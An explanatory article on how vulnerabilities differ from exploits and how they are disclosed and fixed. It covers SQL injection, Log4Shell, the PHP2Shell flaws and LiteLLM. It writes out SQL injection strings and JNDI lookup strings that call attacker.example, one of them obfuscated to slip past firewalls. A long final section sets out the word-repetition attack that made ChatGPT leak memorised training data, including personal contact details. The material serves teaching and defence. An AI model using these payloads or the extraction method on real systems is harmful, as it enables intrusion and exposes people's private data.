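# Exploits and vulnerabilities in deployed AI systems: how to tell them apart, disclose them and fix them

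## What vulnerabilities, exploits and disclosure are

A vulnerability is a weakness in a system that an attacker could use to cause harm. An exploit is a specific, working attack that uses a vulnerability. Computer security specialists distinguish the two because one weakness often allows many attacks, and a fix that stops one attack may not stop the others. AI developers now face the same problem. Companies have released language models (programs that generate text) to hundreds of millions of people, and outside researchers keep finding inputs that make these models do things their developers meant to prevent. When a developer makes a change that stops one of these inputs from working, the underlying weakness may remain, and it is usually harder to establish that the weakness is gone than that the input no longer works.

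Definitions of a vulnerability are similar but vary in breadth. The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) defines it in a glossary entry, NIST's *vulnerability*, as a weakness that a "threat source" could exploit or trigger. The CERT Coordination Center (CERT/CC), a group at Carnegie Mellon University that helps researchers and companies handle vulnerabilities, has a broader definition. CERT/CC's *Vulnerability* defines the term as a set of conditions or behaviours that allows someone to violate a security policy, whether or not the policy is written down. Besides software defects, CERT/CC lists configuration and design decisions, unexpected interactions between systems and changes in the environment as causes. This breadth is useful for AI, where a harmful behaviour may come from training and not correspond to any faulty line of code. But it also means that whether a behaviour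 counts as a vulnerability depends on what the policy was, which people dispute for AI systems. "Flaw" is broader still and covers any condition or behaviour of an AI system that allows a breach of its safety, security or use policy.

CERT/CC's *Exploits, Malware, and Incidents* defines an exploit as software that uses a vulnerability to achieve some effect. The effect may be harmless, since researchers often write exploits only to show that a vulnerability exists. This definition is a little narrow for language models, where the attack is often a typed sentence. Red Hat's *Explaining Security Lingo* says an exploit can be either an executable program or a simple set of commands or instructions, and a typed prompt fits that description.

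### SQL injection as an example

SQL is the standard language for sending commands to databases. Suppose a website shows customers their account balance. The visitor types a name, and the program joins that name to the text of a command:

```
"SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = '" + name + "'"
```

If the visitor types `alice`, the database looks up the balance of the user named alice. But the database receives the programmer's code and the visitor's input as a single string. Only a pair of quote marks separates the two, and a visitor can type a quote mark too. *CWE-89*, an entry in the catalogue of common weaknesses maintained by the American non-profit MITRE, describes how the database may then interpret the visitor's input as SQL instead of as ordinary data. This flaw is the vulnerability, and it exists from the day the programmer writes the line, even if no attacker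 ever visits the site.

An exploit is a particular thing to type. Following MITRE's example, an attacker could enter this as a username:

```
alice'; DELETE FROM user_data; --
```

The quote mark after `alice` closes the name early, and the semicolon ends the lookup. `DELETE FROM user_data` then runs as a second command and empties the table. The two hyphens turn the leftover quote mark into a comment, which the database ignores. MITRE adds that the attack works only on database servers that accept several commands in one batch. On others, such as Oracle's, the string only produces an error, so an exploit can fail even though the system is still vulnerable.

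Now suppose the site's operator, in a hurry, sets up a firewall that rejects any request containing the word DELETE. The attack stops working. This is a block: a measure that stops a known exploit and leaves the vulnerability in place. The attacker's next attempt might be:

```
alice' OR 'a'='a
```

Since `'a'='a'` is true for every row in the table, the database returns everybody's balance. This attack is a variant, a different exploit of the same vulnerability. It contains no DELETE and doesn't need a batch of commands, so it would also work on the servers where the first attack failed.

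The operator can lengthen the list of forbidden words, but MITRE calls such lists "riddled with loopholes". Attackers can target fields that the program does not put in quotes, or find ways to do without the characters that the filter removes. Filtering can also corrupt legitimate data. A program that strips out apostrophes lowers the risk of an attack, but it records the wrong name for a customer called O'Reilly. MITRE still recommends firewalls when a third party controls the code, as an emergency measure while a better repair is under way, or as an extra layer of defence. It rates their effectiveness as moderate.

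Some blocks are much broader than a word filter. MITRE also advises giving the program's database account only the permissions it needs. If the account can read the table but cannot change it, no deletion will succeed, however the attacker spells it. The second attack above still works, though, because the account needs permission to read the table.

The fix is to stop joining strings. With a prepared statement, the programmer writes the command with a placeholder and passes the name separately:

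```
"SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = ?"
```

The *SQL Injection Prevention Cheat Sheet* from the Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit that publishes guidance for programmers, explains why this works. The developer defines all the SQL first and supplies the values afterwards, so the database can always distinguish code from data. If an attacker types `tom' or '1'='1`, the database searches for a user with exactly that name. The programmer doesn't have to foresee this or any other injection attack for the fix to stop it, as they would with a list of forbidden words.

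A fix can still be incomplete. A placeholder cannot stand for the name of a table or column, so OWASP recommends choosing those from a fixed list of permitted names. MITRE warns that programmers can bring the weakness back by assembling and running command strings inside the features that should prevent it. The programmer also has to fix every place where the program builds queries.

In *A Year in Review of 0-days Exploited In-The-Wild in 2020*, Maddie Stone (2021) of Google's Project Zero, which studies previously unknown vulnerabilities, turned this into a two-part standard. A complete patch must be correct, meaning it no longer allows any exploitation of the vulnerability, and comprehensive, meaning it reaches every place that needs it. She observed that vendors often block only the path that the sample exploit takes. Of the 24 zero-days (vulnerabilities that attackers use before the vendor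 has a repair ready) that defenders detected in 2020, six were closely related to vulnerabilities already public. One pair was in the Windows component that handles printing for 32-bit programs. In 2019 an attacker could take control of a memory-copying operation there by sending the component a message of type 0x75. In 2020 an attacker could do the same with a message of type 0x6D whose contents were arranged slightly differently.

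Stone calls the second of these a variant of the first, meaning a closely related vulnerability. Her sense is wider than the one above, where a variant is another exploit of the same vulnerability. The two senses can be hard to separate. The Windows pair, for example, could reasonably be described as one weakness that can be exploited in two ways. The pattern continued in the first half of 2022, when at least nine of the zero-days attackers used were variants, in Stone's wider sense, of vulnerabilities that vendors had already patched (Stone, 2022).

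### The two meanings of "patch"

"Patch" ought to mean a fix, and often does. NIST's *Guide to Enterprise Patch Management Planning* (Souppaya and Scarfone, 2022) defines patching as applying a change to installed software that corrects security or functionality problems or adds new capabilities. But security staff also use the term "virtual patch", which OWASP's *Virtual Patching Cheat Sheet* applies to a layer that intercepts attacks before they reach the application and leaves its source code unchanged. In the example above, the firewall rule against DELETE would be a virtual patch and the prepared statement would be an ordinary one. An operator who had applied either could truthfully tell customers that the site "has a patch".

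Souppaya and Scarfone use "mitigation" both for eliminating a vulnerability and for adding controls, such as firewalls, that make it harder to exploit. But they separate the two when planning. They advise organisations that have put an emergency mitigation in place to plan to replace it with a permanent fix, and to set and enforce a schedule for installing the fix and removing the emergency mitigation. Because the common words blur this distinction, the sections that follow use "block" for a measure that stops a known exploit and "fix" for a change that removes the vulnerability.

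### Coordinated disclosure and embargoes

Someone who finds a vulnerability has to decide whom to tell first. Publishing it immediately warns users but also informs attackers before a fix exists, while staying silent leaves users exposed to anyone else who finds it. The usual compromise is coordinated vulnerability disclosure (CVD), in which the finder tells those who can fix the vulnerability before telling the public, on an agreed schedule. CERT/CC's *The CERT Guide to CVD in a Nutshell* describes the roles involved. The finder discovers the vulnerability and usually reports it. The vendor, which made or maintains the product, checks the report, ranks it against other work and prepares a fix. A coordinator is a third party that may step in when many vendors share the problem or when the finder and vendor disagree. The users, whom CERT/CC calls deployers, then have to install the fix. CERT/CC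 notes that one organisation can hold several of these roles, and that a cloud provider may be both vendor and deployer. A company that runs a language model on its own computers is in that position. It can change the system for every user at once, and users may be unable to see what it changed.

The period of secrecy in the middle is an embargo. CERT/CC's *Embargo Principles* defines it as an informal agreement among the participants not to publish information about the vulnerability until some future point. An embargo needs a definite end date. CERT/CC recommends a length of a few days to a few months, because longer embargoes are more likely to fail, as are those with more participants. Unlike a non-disclosure agreement, an embargo carries no legal penalty. Any participant may leave at any time, though leaving early may make others less willing to cooperate on the next case. No one is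 obliged to publish when the embargo ends.

### What a deployed language model consists of

A language model processes text as tokens, each a word or part of a word. Given a sequence of tokens, the model computes a probability for every token that could come next. The system picks one, adds it to the end of the sequence, and repeats until the reply is complete. The probabilities depend on the model's weights, which are numbers that the developer sets by training. A large model has billions of weights.

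The developer first adjusts the model's weights so that it predicts the next token well across a very large body of text, much of it from the public internet. The result is a base model, which continues whatever text it receives. Given a question, it may well produce more questions, as if continuing an exam paper. Alignment training then adjusts the same weights so that the model follows instructions and refuses some requests. Because this training builds on the base model's weights, much of what the base model could do may remain.

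Memorisation, the capacity to reproduce passages of the training data, is one thing that can survive. An attack that makes a model output such passages is called training-data extraction, and it is a privacy problem if, say, a passage contains somebody's telephone number. Sometimes a chat model stops giving assistant-style answers and produces text like a base model's. This is called divergence, and an attacker may be able to provoke it.

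The weights are only one layer of what a customer uses, and a developer can intervene at any of them.

| Layer | What it does | A change there that could stop an attack |
|---|---|---|
| Application | Takes the user's text, often adds instructions of its own, and displays the reply | Cut off very long replies |
| Programming interface (API) | Passes requests from applications and outside developers to the model; enforces account rules and usage limits | Suspend accounts that send thousands of near-identical requests |
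| Filters | Inspect the prompt before the model receives it, or the reply before the user does | Reject prompts that resemble a known attack |
| Weights | Determine what text the model generates | Train the model to refuse the request, or retrain it without the sensitive passages |

The last row contains two very different repairs. Training a model to refuse one kind of request changes the weights, but it may still be only a block if another prompt can draw out the memorised passages. The layers also work only on requests that pass through them. A length limit in the chat application doesn't affect a developer who reaches the same model through the programming interface, and if a company publishes its weights, anyone can run the model without filters.

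In November 2023, researchers reported extracting training data from ChatGPT by asking it to repeat a single word forever. They wrote that OpenAI could easily stop the attack by training the model to refuse the request or by filtering out prompts that repeat a word many times. But that would patch the exploit without fixing the vulnerability, which in their view was that language models memorise training data and are subject to divergence. Quite different attacks might exploit the same weaknesses. They also used SQL injection as a comparison.

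The comparison holds until someone has to supply the fix. SQL injection has a known fix, and a programmer can check for it by reading the code. Nobody can read a few billion weights to check whether a passage is still stored in them. An outsider who resends last month's attack and gets a refusal learns only that this prompt no longer works through this route. The refusal might come from a filter or new alignment training, or the company might have swapped in another model for unrelated reasons, so the refusal doesn't show what, if anything, the developer repaired.

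## How software security handles a weakness and an attack on it

People who fix ordinary software share public records of its flaws. They keep separate records for types of mistake, particular vulnerabilities, their severity, and whether attackers are using them. An administrator who reads that a vendor has fixed CVE-2021-44228 knows which vulnerability the vendor means, even if the fix later turns out to be incomplete.

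### CWE, CVE, CVSS and the known-exploited list

The Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE) is MITRE's catalogue of types of weakness. CWE-89, for example, covers SQL injection in any program. Programmers consult an entry to avoid a mistake or repair one properly, not to learn whether they need to update something. Code-scanning tools label their findings with CWE numbers.

A CVE identifier, from the Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures programme, refers to a specific vulnerability in a specific product. For example, CIRCL's *CVE-2026-17543*, a record for a vulnerability in the programming language PHP, lists the affected versions as every 8.4 release before 8.4.24 and every 8.5 release before 8.5.9. It also credits the finder and an analyst at the PHP Foundation. Once a record is public, administrators and their scanning tools can check installed versions against it.

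The Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS) rates severity from 0 to 10, and a score of 9 or more counts as critical. The score comes from a short list of judgements about the vulnerability. An early copy of the security page kept by Apache gives these judgements for one of the Log4j vulnerabilities discussed below. The attacker works over the network, the attack is hard to carry out, and it needs no account and no action by a user. The damage can spread beyond the vulnerable component, and the loss of confidentiality, integrity and availability is high in each case. Version 3.1 of the system turns each judgement into a number:

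```
ease of attack = 8.22 × 0.85 × 0.44 × 0.85 × 0.85 ≈ 2.22
impact         ≈ 6.05
score          = 1.08 × (2.22 + 6.05) ≈ 8.93, rounded up to 9.0
```

The 0.44 stands for a difficult attack. An easy one has the value 0.77, which would raise the score to the maximum of 10. Organisations often use these scores to decide what to repair first. But the calculation does not include whether anyone is attacking, so a vulnerability's score is the same whether nobody has used it or criminals use it every day.

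The US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) keeps the Known Exploited Vulnerabilities (KEV) catalogue to fill that gap. SecurityWeek's *CISA Directs Federal Agencies to Prioritize Security Patches Based on Risk* reports that CISA set up the catalogue in 2021 together with a directive, BOD 22-01. The directive required federal agencies to patch the listed vulnerabilities within set periods and report their progress, but did not penalise agencies that missed the deadlines. On 10 June 2026 CISA (2026) issued a new directive, BOD 26-04, which requires agencies to repair high-risk vulnerabilities quickly and lets them defer lower-risk ones. Agencies must have a standing process for repairing whatever CISA adds to the catalogue, according to the legal blog Inside Privacy. Contractors have to comply only if their contracts require it.

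### Log4Shell

Log4j is a free library that Java programs use to write logs. Volunteers at the Apache Software Foundation maintain it. Older versions searched each message for expressions of the form `${...}` and replaced each one with a value, such as the version of Java in use. One kind of expression, a JNDI lookup, could fetch the value from another computer. The code for these lookups dates from 18 July 2013, according to the security company Snyk.

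Programs routinely log text that strangers send them, such as a username or the name of a browser. So an attacker could send this:

```
${jndi:ldap://attacker.example/a}
```

When the program logged the text, Log4j performed the lookup and contacted the attacker's server over LDAP, a protocol for directory services. The server could reply with the location of code, which the program would load and run. As with SQL injection, the software treated untrusted data as instructions. The vulnerability became known as Log4Shell, and Averlon's *CVE-2021-44228* gives its score as 10.

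Alibaba's security team reported it to Apache privately on 24 November 2021, and by Snyk's timeline Apache began work on a repaired version, 2.15.0, five days later. The attack became public around 9 December. Many operators couldn't update at once, often because Log4j was buried inside a product they had bought from someone else. Firewall companies wrote rules to reject any request containing `${jndi:`, and attackers soon sent versions like this one:

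```
${${lower:j}ndi:ldap://attacker.example/a}
```

The inner expression is another lookup, which converts a letter to lower case. Log4j evaluates it first and gets the original attack string, but the firewall rule finds no match for `jndi`. The companies added patterns for the new spellings, and attackers found more. The rules gave more time to operators who had no other defense, and they stopped the many attackers who only copied the published string. They could not block every version, because Log4j's lookup features let attackers keep rewriting the string.

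Apache's first update was also incomplete. Version 2.15.0 turned off lookups in log messages by default. But applications can also store values, such as a visitor's login name, in Log4j's thread context, and some administrators had configured Log4j to insert those values into each log line with a lookup. An attacker who controlled such a value could still get Log4j to interpret it. This flaw received its own identifier, CVE-2021-45046. Apache first described it as a way to make a program stop responding, and its severity score was 3.7. After it became clear that attackers could also run code in some configurations, the score rose to 9.0, as Bitnami's *Security Notices* records. An administrator who sorted repairs by score would at first have put this one near the bottom.

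Apache then released three more versions in December. Bitnami gives the dates for 2.16.0 and 2.17.0, and Apache's notice *Important*, on the Log4j site, describes the last fix.

| Version | Released | What changed | Next problem found |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2.15.0 | Early December 2021 | Turned off lookups in messages by default | Code execution through the thread context in some configurations (CVE-2021-45046) |
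| 2.16.0 | 13 December | Removed lookups in messages; turned off JNDI by default | A crafted value that refers to itself could crash the program (CVE-2021-45105, score 7.5) |
| 2.17.0 | 17 December | Stopped the endless self-reference | A malicious configuration could load remote code (CVE-2021-44832) |
| 2.17.1 | Late December | Limited JNDI data sources to Java's local protocol | – |

The important change came in 2.16.0, when Apache deleted message lookups. After that, no attack string in a message could trigger a lookup, however it was spelled. Turning a feature off leaves its code in place, where some other route could still reach it. Apache later also removed LDAP support from Log4j's JNDI connections, as a change to its security page explains. The two later vulnerabilities were less serious. One caused only a crash, and the other required an attacker who could already change the program's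 configuration.

Even Apache's pages differ on which version fixed each vulnerability. The early copy of the security page and Apache's table of versions both list 2.16.0 as the fix for CVE-2021-45046, but the source text of the security page lists 2.17.0. The table also lists the original Log4Shell vulnerability as present up to 2.16.0, while Apache's first statement gave 2.14.1 as the last affected version. An administrator could avoid the question by installing 2.17.1. But which version removed the vulnerability depends on whether "the vulnerability" means the published attack, any lookup in a log message, or any way for Log4j to load remote code.

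An incomplete fix normally gets its own CVE number. For example, the 2024 release notes for PHP 8.1.28, reproduced by Linux Compatible, list CVE-2024-2756. Developers had only partly fixed CVE-2022-31629, and the incomplete fix left a way around some protections for browser cookies. The number of CVEs can therefore overstate the number of separate weaknesses, and a record marked as fixed doesn't rule out a second record for much the same problem.

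Stone's counts at Google suggest that this happens often among the vulnerabilities attackers actually use. In all of 2022, she counted 17 variants, in her wider sense, among the 41 zero-days detected, a larger share than in 2020. The figures are too rough to show a trend, because they cover only attacks that someone noticed and because deciding what counts as closely related takes judgement. But they suggest that attackers regularly return to code that a vendor has just repaired, where they can use the repair to work out where to look.

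### The PHP flaws of 2024 to 2026

An exploit for Log4Shell was public before most users could install a fix. The maintainers of PHP, by contrast, knew of a weakness for two years without knowing how anyone could attack it.

PHP runs on the servers behind an estimated 70% of websites. The PHP Foundation's *PHP Core Security Audit Results* (2025) describes a 2024 audit of its core by the security company Quarkslab, which Germany's Sovereign Tech Agency commissioned. While repairing what the auditors had found, a developer working for the Foundation noticed signs of another problem, in how PHP behaves when it runs out of memory. @IT's *PHP重大脆弱性は「始まり」に過ぎない* (2026), a Japanese account, explains why the repair stalled. Nobody had found a concrete attack, so clearer problems took priority. Each proposed repair also had a drawback. Some might have broken existing programs or given attackers a way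 to take sites down, and one would have required changes to extensions that other people maintain. The security team wanted the developers to agree on a repair, but they didn't. The Foundation later called this a "structural failure" of its decision-making and resources, according to *Desarrollador PHP urge usar parches para corregir vulnerabilidades críticas en servidores* (2026) in the Paraguayan newspaper ABC Color.

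On 30 July 2026 Calif, a Californian security company, began a new audit at the Foundation's request, using OpenAI's tools. Tom's Hardware's *OpenAI says ChatGPT Sol helped uncover critical PHP flaws* (2026) reports that a Calif researcher identified an exploitable vulnerability on 11 August. It had the same root cause as the 2024 problem, and OpenAI's researchers independently reported that cause the same day. The security company Wiz reported further routes of attack on 24 August, as did OpenAI on 18 September.

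The maintainers assigned two CVE numbers, and both vulnerabilities scored 9.2. In CVE-2026-109618, PHP runs out of memory while setting up its internal data for a request. It abandons the request, and the clean-up code treats the half-finished data as valid. In CVE-2026-109619, PHP keeps a reference to a piece of memory after releasing it. When the same process handles the next request, it may use that reference even though something else now occupies the memory. In either case, an attacker who controls the contents of the memory may be able to run code on the server without logging in.

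It is hard to say how much of this was due to AI. In Help Net Security's *PHP2Shell* (2026), named after the two vulnerabilities' nickname, Wiz's researchers described the necessary chain of steps as "at the edge of what human researchers could practically achieve". OpenAI and Wiz both have an interest in that story. In ITPro's *The PHP incident offers some important lessons for IT leaders*, the consultant Daniel Card said that a human decided where to look, building on an earlier, similar bug. In The Vanguard USA's *PHP2Shell*, Ryan Austin of Calif also cautioned that no model finds every bug "with simple prompts".

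Tom's Hardware objects that the flaws might never have been exploitable without AI and so were effectively harmless until then. That is a fair defence of the maintainers' decision in 2024 to give the problem low priority, since they had limited time and reasonably put problems with known attacks first. But whether an attack is feasible depends on the attackers' tools, and these changed while the weakness stayed the same. Nobody had reason to reconsider that priority until someone produced an exploit.

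The repair took much longer than the exploit. OpenAI said this was because the repair required major changes to the PHP engine. PHP released versions 8.5.12, 8.4.27, 8.3.36 and 8.2.35 on 21 October, 71 days after the first report and within the 90 days that many finders allow before they publish their findings.

An advisory in the PHP project's *News Archive* (2026) lists settings that make attacks harder for anyone who can't update immediately, and explains what each one leaves open. Lifting PHP's own memory limit removes the easiest way to trigger the first vulnerability, but the server itself can still run out of memory. Turning off upload progress tracking "blocks the confirmed session paths but not other variants" of the second. Turning off a PHP 8.5 feature that records how an error arose blocks only one confirmed route. The release notes state that there are no complete mitigations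 and that updating is the only safe choice.

Firewalls were less effective against this attack than against Log4Shell because they had no equivalent of `${jndi:` to look for. Fastly, which sells firewall filtering, writes in *PHP2Shell* that there is "no payload string to match", because the attack consists of making a request fail at a precise moment. An ordinary large upload might resemble an attack. Cloudflare, which filters traffic for many websites, had rules for the known routes of attack in place about nine hours before the announcement, but attackers changed their requests to get past them, according to Dmytro's guide for a hosting company, also titled *PHP2Shell*.

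The secrecy around the release broke down in the last day before it. According to Fastly's timeline, the two CVE numbers began to circulate at about 15:00 UTC on 20 October, and PHP moved the release forward from 22 to 21 October. Calif then published a video of its exploit by mistake. At 03:59 on 21 October, Fastly recorded the first scanning tool named after the vulnerability. At 07:41, Chainguard, a company that had received the repair in advance, published software containing it, more than six hours before everyone else could update. By the time the updates came out at 14:00, scans using such tools had come from more than 100 internet addresses. Senders had labelled about a third of the traffic Fastly stored up to midday on 22 October as defensive checking.

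The damage so far seems smaller than one would expect from the number of attacks. Cloudflare's chief executive reported millions of attempts, but about three weeks after the release ITPro found only a handful of confirmed break-ins, mainly through Palo Alto firewalls whose administration pages were open to the internet. In one serious breach, hackers with suspected links to China used the flaws to enter a network affiliated with the US government, according to Cybernews' *PHP won't let admins catch a break* (2026). The article also cites an estimate by Censys, which surveys the internet, that more than half of some 50 million exposed servers still lacked the update in mid-November.

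Soon after the October releases, PHP disclosed CVE-2026-115560, another way to run code through the upload-progress feature, which affected even fully updated servers. It requires an application to change how it stores session data while running, which is unusual, so PHP left the fix for its regular release on 19 November. Until then, it told users to turn off upload progress, one of the measures it had suggested in October. Administrators who had updated but left the feature off had nothing more to do. Souppaya and Scarfone advise organisations to remove emergency measures once the permanent fix is in, and this case is a reason to check for variants first.

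### From an exploit to a tested repair

Good practice begins with root-cause analysis, working back from the exploit to the mistake that made it possible. In the PHP case, this let the maintainers recognise when different researchers had reported the same problem. This was necessary because the security team had, according to @IT, dealt with more than 100 invalid, duplicate or unreproducible reports since July. The Foundation used AI tools to check reports and group those with a common cause, but a person made each decision and worked on each patch.

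Defenders who know the cause of a vulnerability can search for variants before attackers do. Calif's *MAD Bugs* describes one such search in `unserialize()`, a PHP function that rebuilds stored data. Calif's researchers gave Claude, Anthropic's language model, about 20 old security advisories for the function and had it sort them by type of bug. They then used the model to look for the same types in PHP 8.5.5 and found a vulnerability that had been in PHP for 21 years. PHP's developers had earlier decided to stop treating memory errors in this function as security vulnerabilities, because programs should never give it untrusted data. They would still fix the errors, but without urgency or CVE numbers, so a search limited to CVE records would have missed some of the history.

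A temporary block, such as a firewall rule, can protect users during the search and the repair. The fix then has to remove the cause. Developers also add a regression test, which runs automatically whenever someone changes the program and fails if the problem has returned. A test that only replays the original exploit is a poor one, because a program with just a temporary block would pass it. In the SQL example, a filter on the word DELETE would be enough to pass. A better test sends several variants of the attack, or checks directly that the program never runs a visitor's text as a command.

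A failed repair to LiteLLM in 2026 shows what can happen without such a test. Companies use LiteLLM to connect their systems to various AI models. In versions 1.74.2 to 1.83.6, its feature for testing connections to outside tools accepted a complete configuration from the user, including a command to run, according to Action1's *CVE-2026-42271*. Anyone with a valid key, even one with few privileges, could therefore run commands on the server. Indusface's *CVE-2026-42271* reports that the repaired version, 1.83.7, allows only administrators to use the feature.

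According to the Swedish magazine Elektroniktidningen, researchers at TrendAI, who had reported a vulnerability in LiteLLM, examined the update and bypassed it in less than a second. The version history showed that the developers had used AI to write the patch. In TrendAI's view, language models tend to apply the common, well-documented remedy for a type of vulnerability, which may stop one attack without removing the cause. The description of the update fits that explanation. Restricting a feature to administrators is a standard remedy for missing access control, but the feature still runs whatever command it receives, so the access check is the only protection. Human programmers make the same mistake, as Log4j 2.15.0 shows, and one failed patch isn't enough to show that AI makes it more often. TrendAI recommends treating AI-written patches as suggestions and testing them against real attacks.

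The LiteLLM vulnerability scored 8.7, just short of critical, but it is on CISA's list because attackers are using it. TrendAI's decoy servers recorded attempts to steal passwords for cloud services. Of the 4,459 LiteLLM installations that TrendAI found on the internet, 65% ran a version older than the patch, and the rest had a patch that didn't fully protect them.

Users also need to confirm that a fix has reached their own machines. Christiaan Beek of the security company Rapid7 told ITPro that many teams found this the hardest part after the PHP release. Some suppliers add a fix to an old version without changing its number in the expected way, and some servers don't reveal a version at all, so outside scans flagged some fixed servers as vulnerable and missed some vulnerable ones. Even an updated server keeps running the vulnerable code until someone restarts the PHP processes already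 in memory.

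## Tracing the ChatGPT word-repetition attack to its causes

PHP's maintainers could trace an exploit to its cause by reading their own code. The outside researchers who attacked ChatGPT had neither the model's weights nor its training data, so they could only send it text and study the replies. Even so, their paper, *Scalable Extraction of Training Data from (Production) Language Models* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2023), partly explains why repeating a word made the model output its training data. Two 2025 studies explain more. One examines how repetition disrupts a model, and the other extracts memorised text without repetition.

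### The attack

The usual way to extract training data from a base model is to give it a short piece of text and let it continue. Nasr and colleagues first tried this on models whose weights anyone can download. They prompted each model with random five-token sequences from Wikipedia and collected a billion tokens of output. Depending on the model, between 0.03% and 1.4% of those tokens belonged to memorised passages.

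The same method got almost nothing from gpt-3.5-turbo, the version of ChatGPT that OpenAI offered to developers through its programming interface. Only 0.02% of 50 million tokens of output belonged to memorised passages, compared with 0.85% for gpt-3.5-turbo-instruct, an OpenAI model that is presumably similar in size and follows instructions but doesn't hold conversations. One obstacle was the chat format. The service places each message inside a conversation and signals that it is the assistant's turn, so the model starts a reply instead of continuing the user's text. The other obstacle was alignment training. When the researchers asked the model to continue a sentence about the number of staff at the BBC, it replied that they hadn't provided complete information, although it had memorised the passage.

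Alignment training had not solved the problem, though the results up to that point could have suggested it had. In July 2023 Milad Nasr had come across a request that made ChatGPT behave unexpectedly. In the published example, the prompt was to repeat the word "poem" forever. The model did so several hundred times and then diverged. Much of the text that followed was nonsense, but some of it came word for word from the web, including one person's email signature with their contact details. *Between Randomness and Arbitrariness* (2024), the doctoral thesis of the co-author A. Feder Cooper, adds that the model diverged almost every time, but only a fraction of the outputs contained training data. Several people outside the team noticed the same behaviour in early August but, like the team at first, didn't realise what the text was.

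The attack worked only with words that form a single token. When given a word of several tokens, the model either kept repeating it or replied that doing so would not be productive. Some single-token words drew out memorised text over 100 times more often than others. The researchers could measure the underlying effect on gpt-3.5-turbo-instruct because OpenAI published that model's probabilities for each token. After about 250 repetitions of a single-token word, the probability of one more repetition fell rapidly from 90% to below 0.1%. With words of two or three tokens, it stayed above 99% even after several thousand repetitions.

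### How the researchers recognised memorised text

A language model can invent a plausible email signature, so the team needed a way to tell memorised text from invented text. They counted an output as memorised if it contained at least 50 consecutive tokens, or roughly 38 words, that also appeared word for word in existing text. To choose this threshold, they compared older training data with news articles written later. Apart from direct quotations, they found no overlap longer than 25 tokens, and they doubled that number to be safe. They also excluded text with little variety, such as lists of numbers, which might match by accident. Other thresholds changed the totals but left the ranking of the models much the same.

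OpenAI doesn't publish its training data, so there was no original to compare the outputs with. The researchers instead merged four large public collections of training text, most of it from the web, into a dataset of nine terabytes. To search it quickly, they built a suffix array. A suffix is the part of a text that runs from some point to the end, and a suffix array puts all the suffixes in alphabetical order. For the word "banana", the order is:

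```
a, ana, anana, banana, na, nana
```

Any string that occurs in the text is the beginning of at least one suffix. To look for "nan", a program can start in the middle of the array and discard half of the remaining entries at each step, much as a person looks up a word in a dictionary. In a text of nine terabytes, this takes about 43 steps instead of trillions of comparisons. The array stores only the position where each suffix starts, but it still took up 45 terabytes, so the team split it into 32 parts that each fitted into a computer's memory. Building the array and running all the searches took three weeks on one large rented machine.

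A match of this length is strong evidence of memorisation, but the lack of a match is only weak evidence against it, because ChatGPT's training data surely included text outside the nine terabytes. To see how many memorised outputs the automatic search missed, the researchers searched Google by hand for 494 of the outputs. They found 150 of them online, while the automatic search had found 70. The manual search also accepted near-copies, which explains some of the gap, but the result still suggests that the automatic counts are well below the true ones.

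An attacker without such an index would have to guess which outputs were memorised. Nasr and colleagues tested a method that compares how well the model can predict a passage with how far an ordinary compression program can shrink it. A passage that is hard to compress but easy for the model to predict is more likely to be memorised. When they checked manually, only about 30% of the passages the method selected were on the web, so an attacker would still have been wrong more often than right, although they describe the method as highly precise.

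### How much the attack extracted

The researchers extracted over 10,000 different memorised passages with $200 worth of queries. The longest, a website's terms of service, was over 4,000 characters long. The passages included complete poems, parts of novels, program code, the abstract of a paper in *Nature* and an exact bitcoin address. An extended version of the study, *Scalable Extraction of Training Data from Aligned, Production Language Models* (Nasr, Rando and colleagues, ICLR 2025), gives a more precise count of 27,171 passages for the same $200.

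Nearly 3% of the tokens ChatGPT produced under attack were memorised text, which is 150 times its rate with ordinary prompts and about three times the rate of gpt-3.5-turbo-instruct. The multiple of 150 is uncertain because the rate with ordinary prompts is so small. In a later test with only 1,000 ordinary prompts, the 2025 version reports that rate as 0.08% instead of 0.02%, which would reduce the multiple to about 36. The same test put gpt-3.5-turbo-instruct at 2.48%, close to the chat model's rate under attack. The attack clearly made the chat model leak far more, but how its leakage compares with that of a model without chat training depends on the test.

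The percentages reported for personal data are shares of outputs, not of people. Nasr and colleagues searched 15,000 outputs for names with birthdates, addresses, phone numbers and similar details, then checked these against their dataset to confirm that the model had not made them up. They report that 16.9% of the outputs they tested, which would be about 2,500, contained memorised personal information, but that they recovered information about only dozens of individuals. When an output appeared to contain personal information, it was genuine in 85.8% of cases, so an attacker who wanted contact details would have had much less guessing to do. In the 2025 version, which uses a narrower measure, 1,455 of 15,309 outputs (9.5%) contained phone numbers or email addresses.

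The model had almost certainly memorised much more than the team extracted. Over 93% of the memorised passages appeared only once in the outputs, a sign that many more remained to be found. A standard statistical estimate based on how often passages repeated gave a minimum of 1.5 million different 50-token sequences, but the researchers advised against relying on it because the method works badly with such a small sample. They preferred a comparison with GPT-Neo, an open model that they had queried far more heavily. If ChatGPT followed the same pattern, which nobody outside OpenAI could check, it had memorised hundreds of millions of such sequences, or about a gigabyte of text.

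### How alignment training hid the memorisation

This exploit relied on two vulnerabilities, memorisation and divergence, and the researchers could show that memorisation existed independently of the prompt. They took the 1,000 longest passages they had extracted, gave ChatGPT each one without its last 50 tokens and asked it to supply the rest. It completed only 3.5% exactly and came close in another 4%, even though it had produced all of them under attack. Given the same beginnings, gpt-3.5-turbo-instruct completed 75%.

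The two models had probably received different later training, yet both could reproduce the same passages. The researchers concluded that the passages came from the original training on web text, and that alignment training had made the chat model unlikely to output them without removing them from the weights. The test used only passages that had already leaked, so the 75% doesn't estimate how much of its training data the model had memorised. The comparison also can't fully separate the effect of alignment training from that of the chat format, because the two models differed in both. But it does show that someone who tested ChatGPT in the ordinary way, by asking it to complete known texts, would have found almost nothing wrong, while a tester with access to the base model would have had a much better chance of finding the problem.

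The researchers mainly suggested that ChatGPT had memorised so much because OpenAI had trained it on the same text many times. A company that serves a model to millions of people has a reason to do this, because a small model with a lot of training is cheaper to run than a large one with less. Good web text is limited, so long training means repeating it. The team tested models that other researchers had trained on repeated data and confirmed that more passes over the data led to more extractable text, but they could not confirm that OpenAI had trained ChatGPT this way.

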